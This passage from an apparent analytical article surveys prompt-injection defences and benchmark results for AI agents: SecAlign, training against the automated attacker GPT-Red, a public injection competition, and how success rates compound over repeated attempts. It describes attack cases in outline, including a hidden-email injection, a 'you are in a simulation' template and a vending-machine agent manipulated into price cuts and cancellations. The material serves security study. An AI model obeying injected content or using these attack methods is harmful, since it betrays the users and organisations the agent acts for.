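Here P is the probability the model gives each answer, and training measures how much the gap has changed from the original model's. SecAlign therefore teaches the model which answers to avoid as well as which to write.

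StruQ and SecAlign stopped most simple injections in their developers' tests, which used small open-weight models and short tasks. These results are now mainly of historical interest because Nasr and colleagues used adaptive attacks to get past StruQ and Meta's version of SecAlign in 2025.

### Training against an automated attacker

Training on a fixed set of examples teaches a model to resist the attacks in that set, but not necessarily others. Developers have therefore turned to reinforcement learning, in which the model attempts a task, receives a score and becomes more likely to repeat behaviour that scored well. For Claude Opus 4.5, released in late 2025, Anthropic put injections in simulated web content and rewarded the model when it recognised them and refused to comply.

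OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes a model trained to write prompt injection attacks. In each training scenario, GPT-Red controlled one piece of outside content, such as part of a file, the body of an email or the output of a tool, and earned a reward when its attack worked. The defending models trained at the same time and earned a reward for resisting the attack and completing the user's task. As the defenders improved, GPT-Red had to find new attacks.

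OpenAI then used the finished GPT-Red to generate injections to train GPT-5.6. OpenAI reports that this training did not harm the model's ordinary abilities or make it start refusing legitimate requests. One type of attack, which imitates the model's own reasoning, succeeded more than 95% of the time against GPT-5.1 but less than 10% of the time against GPT-5.6 Sol, the largest model in the GPT-5.6 family.

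GPT-Red also attacked an AI agent that ran a vending machine in OpenAI's office. It practised on a simulation, then used the resulting attack on the real agent. The agent cut the price of an expensive item to $0.50, ordered a new item worth over $100 to sell for $0.50, and cancelled another customer's order.

### The competition published in March 2026

*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on a three-week public competition with $40,000 in prizes. The security company Gray Swan ran it with AI developers and the British and American government institutes for AI security. The 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts on 13 models in 41 scenarios, of which 8,648 (3.2%) succeeded.

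In each scenario, the participant wrote text for one place that an outsider could plausibly control, such as an email or a code comment. In most scenarios, an attack succeeded only if the agent took a specified harmful action and its reply gave the user no sign of it. In one scenario, a user asked for a list of urgent emails, and a successful injection in a marketing email made the agent mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the list.

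| Type of agent | Scenarios | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Agents that call tools, such as email or shopping | 18 | 4.82% |
| Agents that operate a computer through its screen | 8 | 3.13% |
| Coding agents | 15 | 2.51% |

The coding scenarios used copies of real open-source projects and transcripts of real coding sessions. Dziemian and colleagues suggest that models did better in these scenarios because the transcripts resembled the models' safety training. If so, training on realistic material helps, but a coding agent in an unusual setting might do worse.

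Attacks succeeded most often against Gemini 2.5 Pro, at a rate of 8.5%, and at least one worked in each of the 37 scenarios that counted towards the final results. They succeeded least often against Claude Opus 4.5, at a rate of 0.5%, and worked in 13 of the 37 scenarios. General ability was a poor guide to resistance, and the researchers think the way a company trains its models matters more. Special training alone was not enough, since the one model of the 13 that Meta had trained with SecAlign was notably less resistant than the Claude and GPT models.

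After the competition, the researchers ran 2,679 of the successful attacks on all the models. The 44 attacks that had beaten Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded between 44% and 81% of the time on the others, while attacks that had beaten Alibaba's Qwen3 VL never worked on Claude Opus 4.5. Attacks that beat weak models are therefore a poor test of strong ones. One template, which told the agent it was in a simulation, needed only small changes to work in 21 scenarios and on nine models.

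Dziemian and colleagues describe the competition's success rates as an upper bound for single-turn attacks, because participants could see the conversation and knew exactly which action to cause. They also had vendors switch off any filters that normally protect the models. But the rates average over many weak attempts, and a better attacker could exceed them. In OpenAI's copy of the competition, GPT-Red succeeded against GPT-5.1 in 84% of scenarios, compared with 13% for human attackers.

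The 13% seems low. The set of 2,679 attacks includes 109 that people had used successfully against GPT-5.1, with at most nine from any scenario, so people must have succeeded in at least 13 of the 41 scenarios, or about a third. OpenAI's copy may have differed from the original. Even if people succeeded in a third of the scenarios, GPT-Red did much better.

### One model, several success rates

Published success rates for the same model vary widely with the choice of attacks.

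| Test of Claude Opus 4.5 | Success rate per attempt |
|---|---|
| All attempts in the competition | 0.5% |
| The 2,679 attacks that had beaten at least one model | 2.5% |
| "Very strong" attacks in an earlier Gray Swan benchmark | 4.7% |
| Anthropic's browser test, model alone | 8.0% |
| Anthropic's browser test, with improved safeguards | 1.4% |

The 4.7% comes from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*.

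Developers disclose different amounts about their injection testing, which makes their models hard to compare. According to VentureBeat, Anthropic's system card for Claude Opus 4.8 covered four kinds of agent use, OpenAI's for GPT-5.5 gave a single score for known attacks, and Google's documents for Gemini 3 included no injection test.

### Claude Opus 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol

The best available comparison is in Anthropic's system card for Claude Opus 5, which reports results from a newer Gray Swan benchmark with 28 scenarios and 1,130 attacks. Anthropic and its partners selected attacks that had worked on several models. The table shows the chance that an attacker succeeds at least once in 15 attempts.

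| Model | Success within 15 attempts |
|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 2.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 5.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 5.9% |
| Muse Spark (Meta) | 16.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 20.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 20.8% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 30.4% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 43.9% |

Anthropic tested its own models without extra safeguards and the others through their public services, which may include such safeguards. This difference could only have helped its competitors. Anthropic has an interest in the result, but the benchmark's attacks came from a competition that several developers and both government institutes supported.

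Although OpenAI had trained GPT-5.6 Sol against GPT-Red, it did barely better than GPT-5.5. This suggests that the latest round of training helped much less against other people's attacks than against GPT-Red's own. It does not show that the method fails, because OpenAI had trained earlier models against weaker versions of GPT-Red.

OpenAI's own figures are therefore harder to interpret. The *GPT-5.6 System Card* (2026) gives GPT-5.6 Sol a perfect score of 1.000 on known attacks through connected apps and 0.910 on stronger attacks through search and function calls. In August, OpenAI added results for attacks by GPT-Red. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that direct attacks succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol about 0.05% of the time, and indirect attacks, the relevant kind for document review and coding, 3.77% of the time.

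The 3.77% is an average per attempt, so it is not comparable with Claude Opus 5's 2.0%, which measures success within 15 attempts. On Gray Swan's benchmark, a single attempt succeeded 3.1% of the time against GPT-5.6 Sol and 0.2% against Claude Opus 5.

The two companies' tests also rank the GPT-5.6 models in opposite orders. In OpenAI's indirect test, Luna did best at 2.94%, followed by Terra at 3.32%. On Gray Swan's benchmark, Luna did much worse than the other two. Luna also did worse than Terra in Nakibly and Babo's replay of real GitHub attacks, which fits Gray Swan's order better. A company that chose among these models using only OpenAI's figures might pick the weakest.

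Anthropic also tested its models against attackers that improve by trial and error. The table gives the share of successful attempts and, in brackets, the number of scenarios in which at least one attempt worked. All the models used extended reasoning.

| Setting | Claude Opus 4.8, no safeguards | Claude Opus 5, no safeguards | Claude Opus 5, with safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coding | 7.03% (23 of 40) | 0.56% (13 of 40) | 0.18% (4 of 40) |
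| Operating a computer | 7.14% (7 of 14) | 0.54% (1 of 14) | 0.25% (1 of 14) |
| Browsing | 31.5% (81 of 129) | 3.70% (11 of 129) | 0% (0 of 129) |

The safeguards in the first two rows are "probes", which check tool results for injected instructions before the model acts. The browser test uses auto mode, which combines probes with the classifier that blocks dangerous actions. The right-hand column therefore measures a product rather than a model, unlike the middle columns.

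The improvement in coding may be partly due to how the test was run. Gray Swan's automated attacker had practised on the same 40 scenarios against an earlier set of models before Anthropic used it on the new ones. An attacker that practised against Claude Opus 5 itself would probably do better.

These results date from July and August 2026 and do not cover newer models such as Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra.

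### The arithmetic of repeated attempts

If each attempt has the same chance of success, *p*, and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in *k* attempts is

1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*

Claude Opus 4.5's rate would then rise from 4.7% after one attempt to 38% after 10 and 99% after 100. The Decoder reports measured rates of 33.6% after 10 attempts and 63% after 100. The next table makes the same comparison for other models, using the single-attempt rates from Gray Swan's newer benchmark.

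| Model | One attempt | Number of attempts | Calculated | Measured |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 10 | 38% | 33.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 100 | 99% | 63% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 15 | 38% | 20.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 15 | 7% | 5.5% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 15 | 3% | 2.0% |

The measured rates are lower mainly because some scenarios are much harder to attack than others. Suppose that each attempt has a 7.5% chance of success in 63% of scenarios and no chance in the remaining 37%. The average for one attempt is

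0.63 × 7.5% ≈ 4.7%

After 10 attempts, the attacker has succeeded in about 54% of the vulnerable scenarios, or 34% of all scenarios. After 100 attempts, the attacker has succeeded in almost all the vulnerable ones, and the overall success rate cannot rise above 63%. This simple model closely matches the measured figures for Claude Opus 4.5. Other mixtures would fit too, so the figures do not prove that any scenario is completely safe. An attacker may be able to succeed in the remaining 37% with better attacks or more than 100 attempts.

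Anthropic tested Claude Opus 5's computer use with 200 prompt injection attempts in each of 14 scenarios. Of the 2,800 attempts, 0.54% succeeded, or about 15. All of them were in the same scenario, where roughly one attempt in 13 succeeded.

An average success rate is therefore a poor guide to a particular company's risk. A persistent attacker will probably succeed if the company's assistant resembles the one weak scenario, but may fail even after many attempts if it resembles the others. The company can find out which case applies only by testing its own assistant.

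### Is the problem nearly solved?

There is a reasonable case that the best models can now resist injected instructions. In Anthropic's three trial-and-error tests, the success rate of attacks was about eight to 13 times lower against Claude Opus 5 than against a model released about two months earlier. With auto mode on, no attack in the browser test succeeded. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* took this result as a sign that the problem might be over for browser agents, but noted that it depended on auto mode. The Wharton study had already found that Claude Opus 4.5 mostly ignored simple demands for higher marks, so the resistance extends to some tasks that involve judgement.

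Schneier on Security is more cautious, saying that preventing prompt injection is impossible in general but that developers are getting much better at blocking it in specific cases. One reader objected that nobody has proved it impossible, and that a different kind of model might separate trusted text from untrusted text. The objection seems correct about future models, but the test results fit the claim of progress in specific cases well.

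A model that scores well on a fixed benchmark can do poorly on another test, even one by the same company. Claude Mythos 5 came second in the Gray Swan table, with an attack success rate of 2.6% within 15 attempts. In the browser test, without safeguards, 29.7% of attempts against it succeeded, and at least one succeeded in 71 of the 129 scenarios. The first result alone would suggest that it was almost as safe as Claude Opus 5.

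Anthropic warns that fixed sets of known attacks can give a "false sense of security". It stopped reporting an older Gray Swan benchmark because its models had scored at or near the best possible result for several releases, and the newer benchmark may soon become too easy too. Earlier system cards included a contest in which people attacked the latest model directly, but Anthropic was still preparing the contest for Claude Opus 5 when it published that model's card.

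The browser test recorded no successful attacks in 129 scenarios, but the true success rate in similar scenarios could still be as high as about 2.3%, and other kinds of attack could succeed more often. The AI Now Institute's demonstration in July got past auto mode with other Claude models.

Even a low success rate can matter when many people use the same assistant. If 100,000 agents read a web page with a payload that works 0.2% of the time, about 200 of them will obey it. This expected number depends only on the average success rate, so it stays the same even if some agents are harder to attack than others. The attacker needs just one page and does not have to know which agents are vulnerable.

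Many organisations will also use cheaper models such as GPT-5.6 Luna, against which Gray Swan's attacks succeeded within 15 attempts 43.9% of the time. These organisations still need the filters and permission limits that a user of Claude Opus 5 might be tempted to drop.
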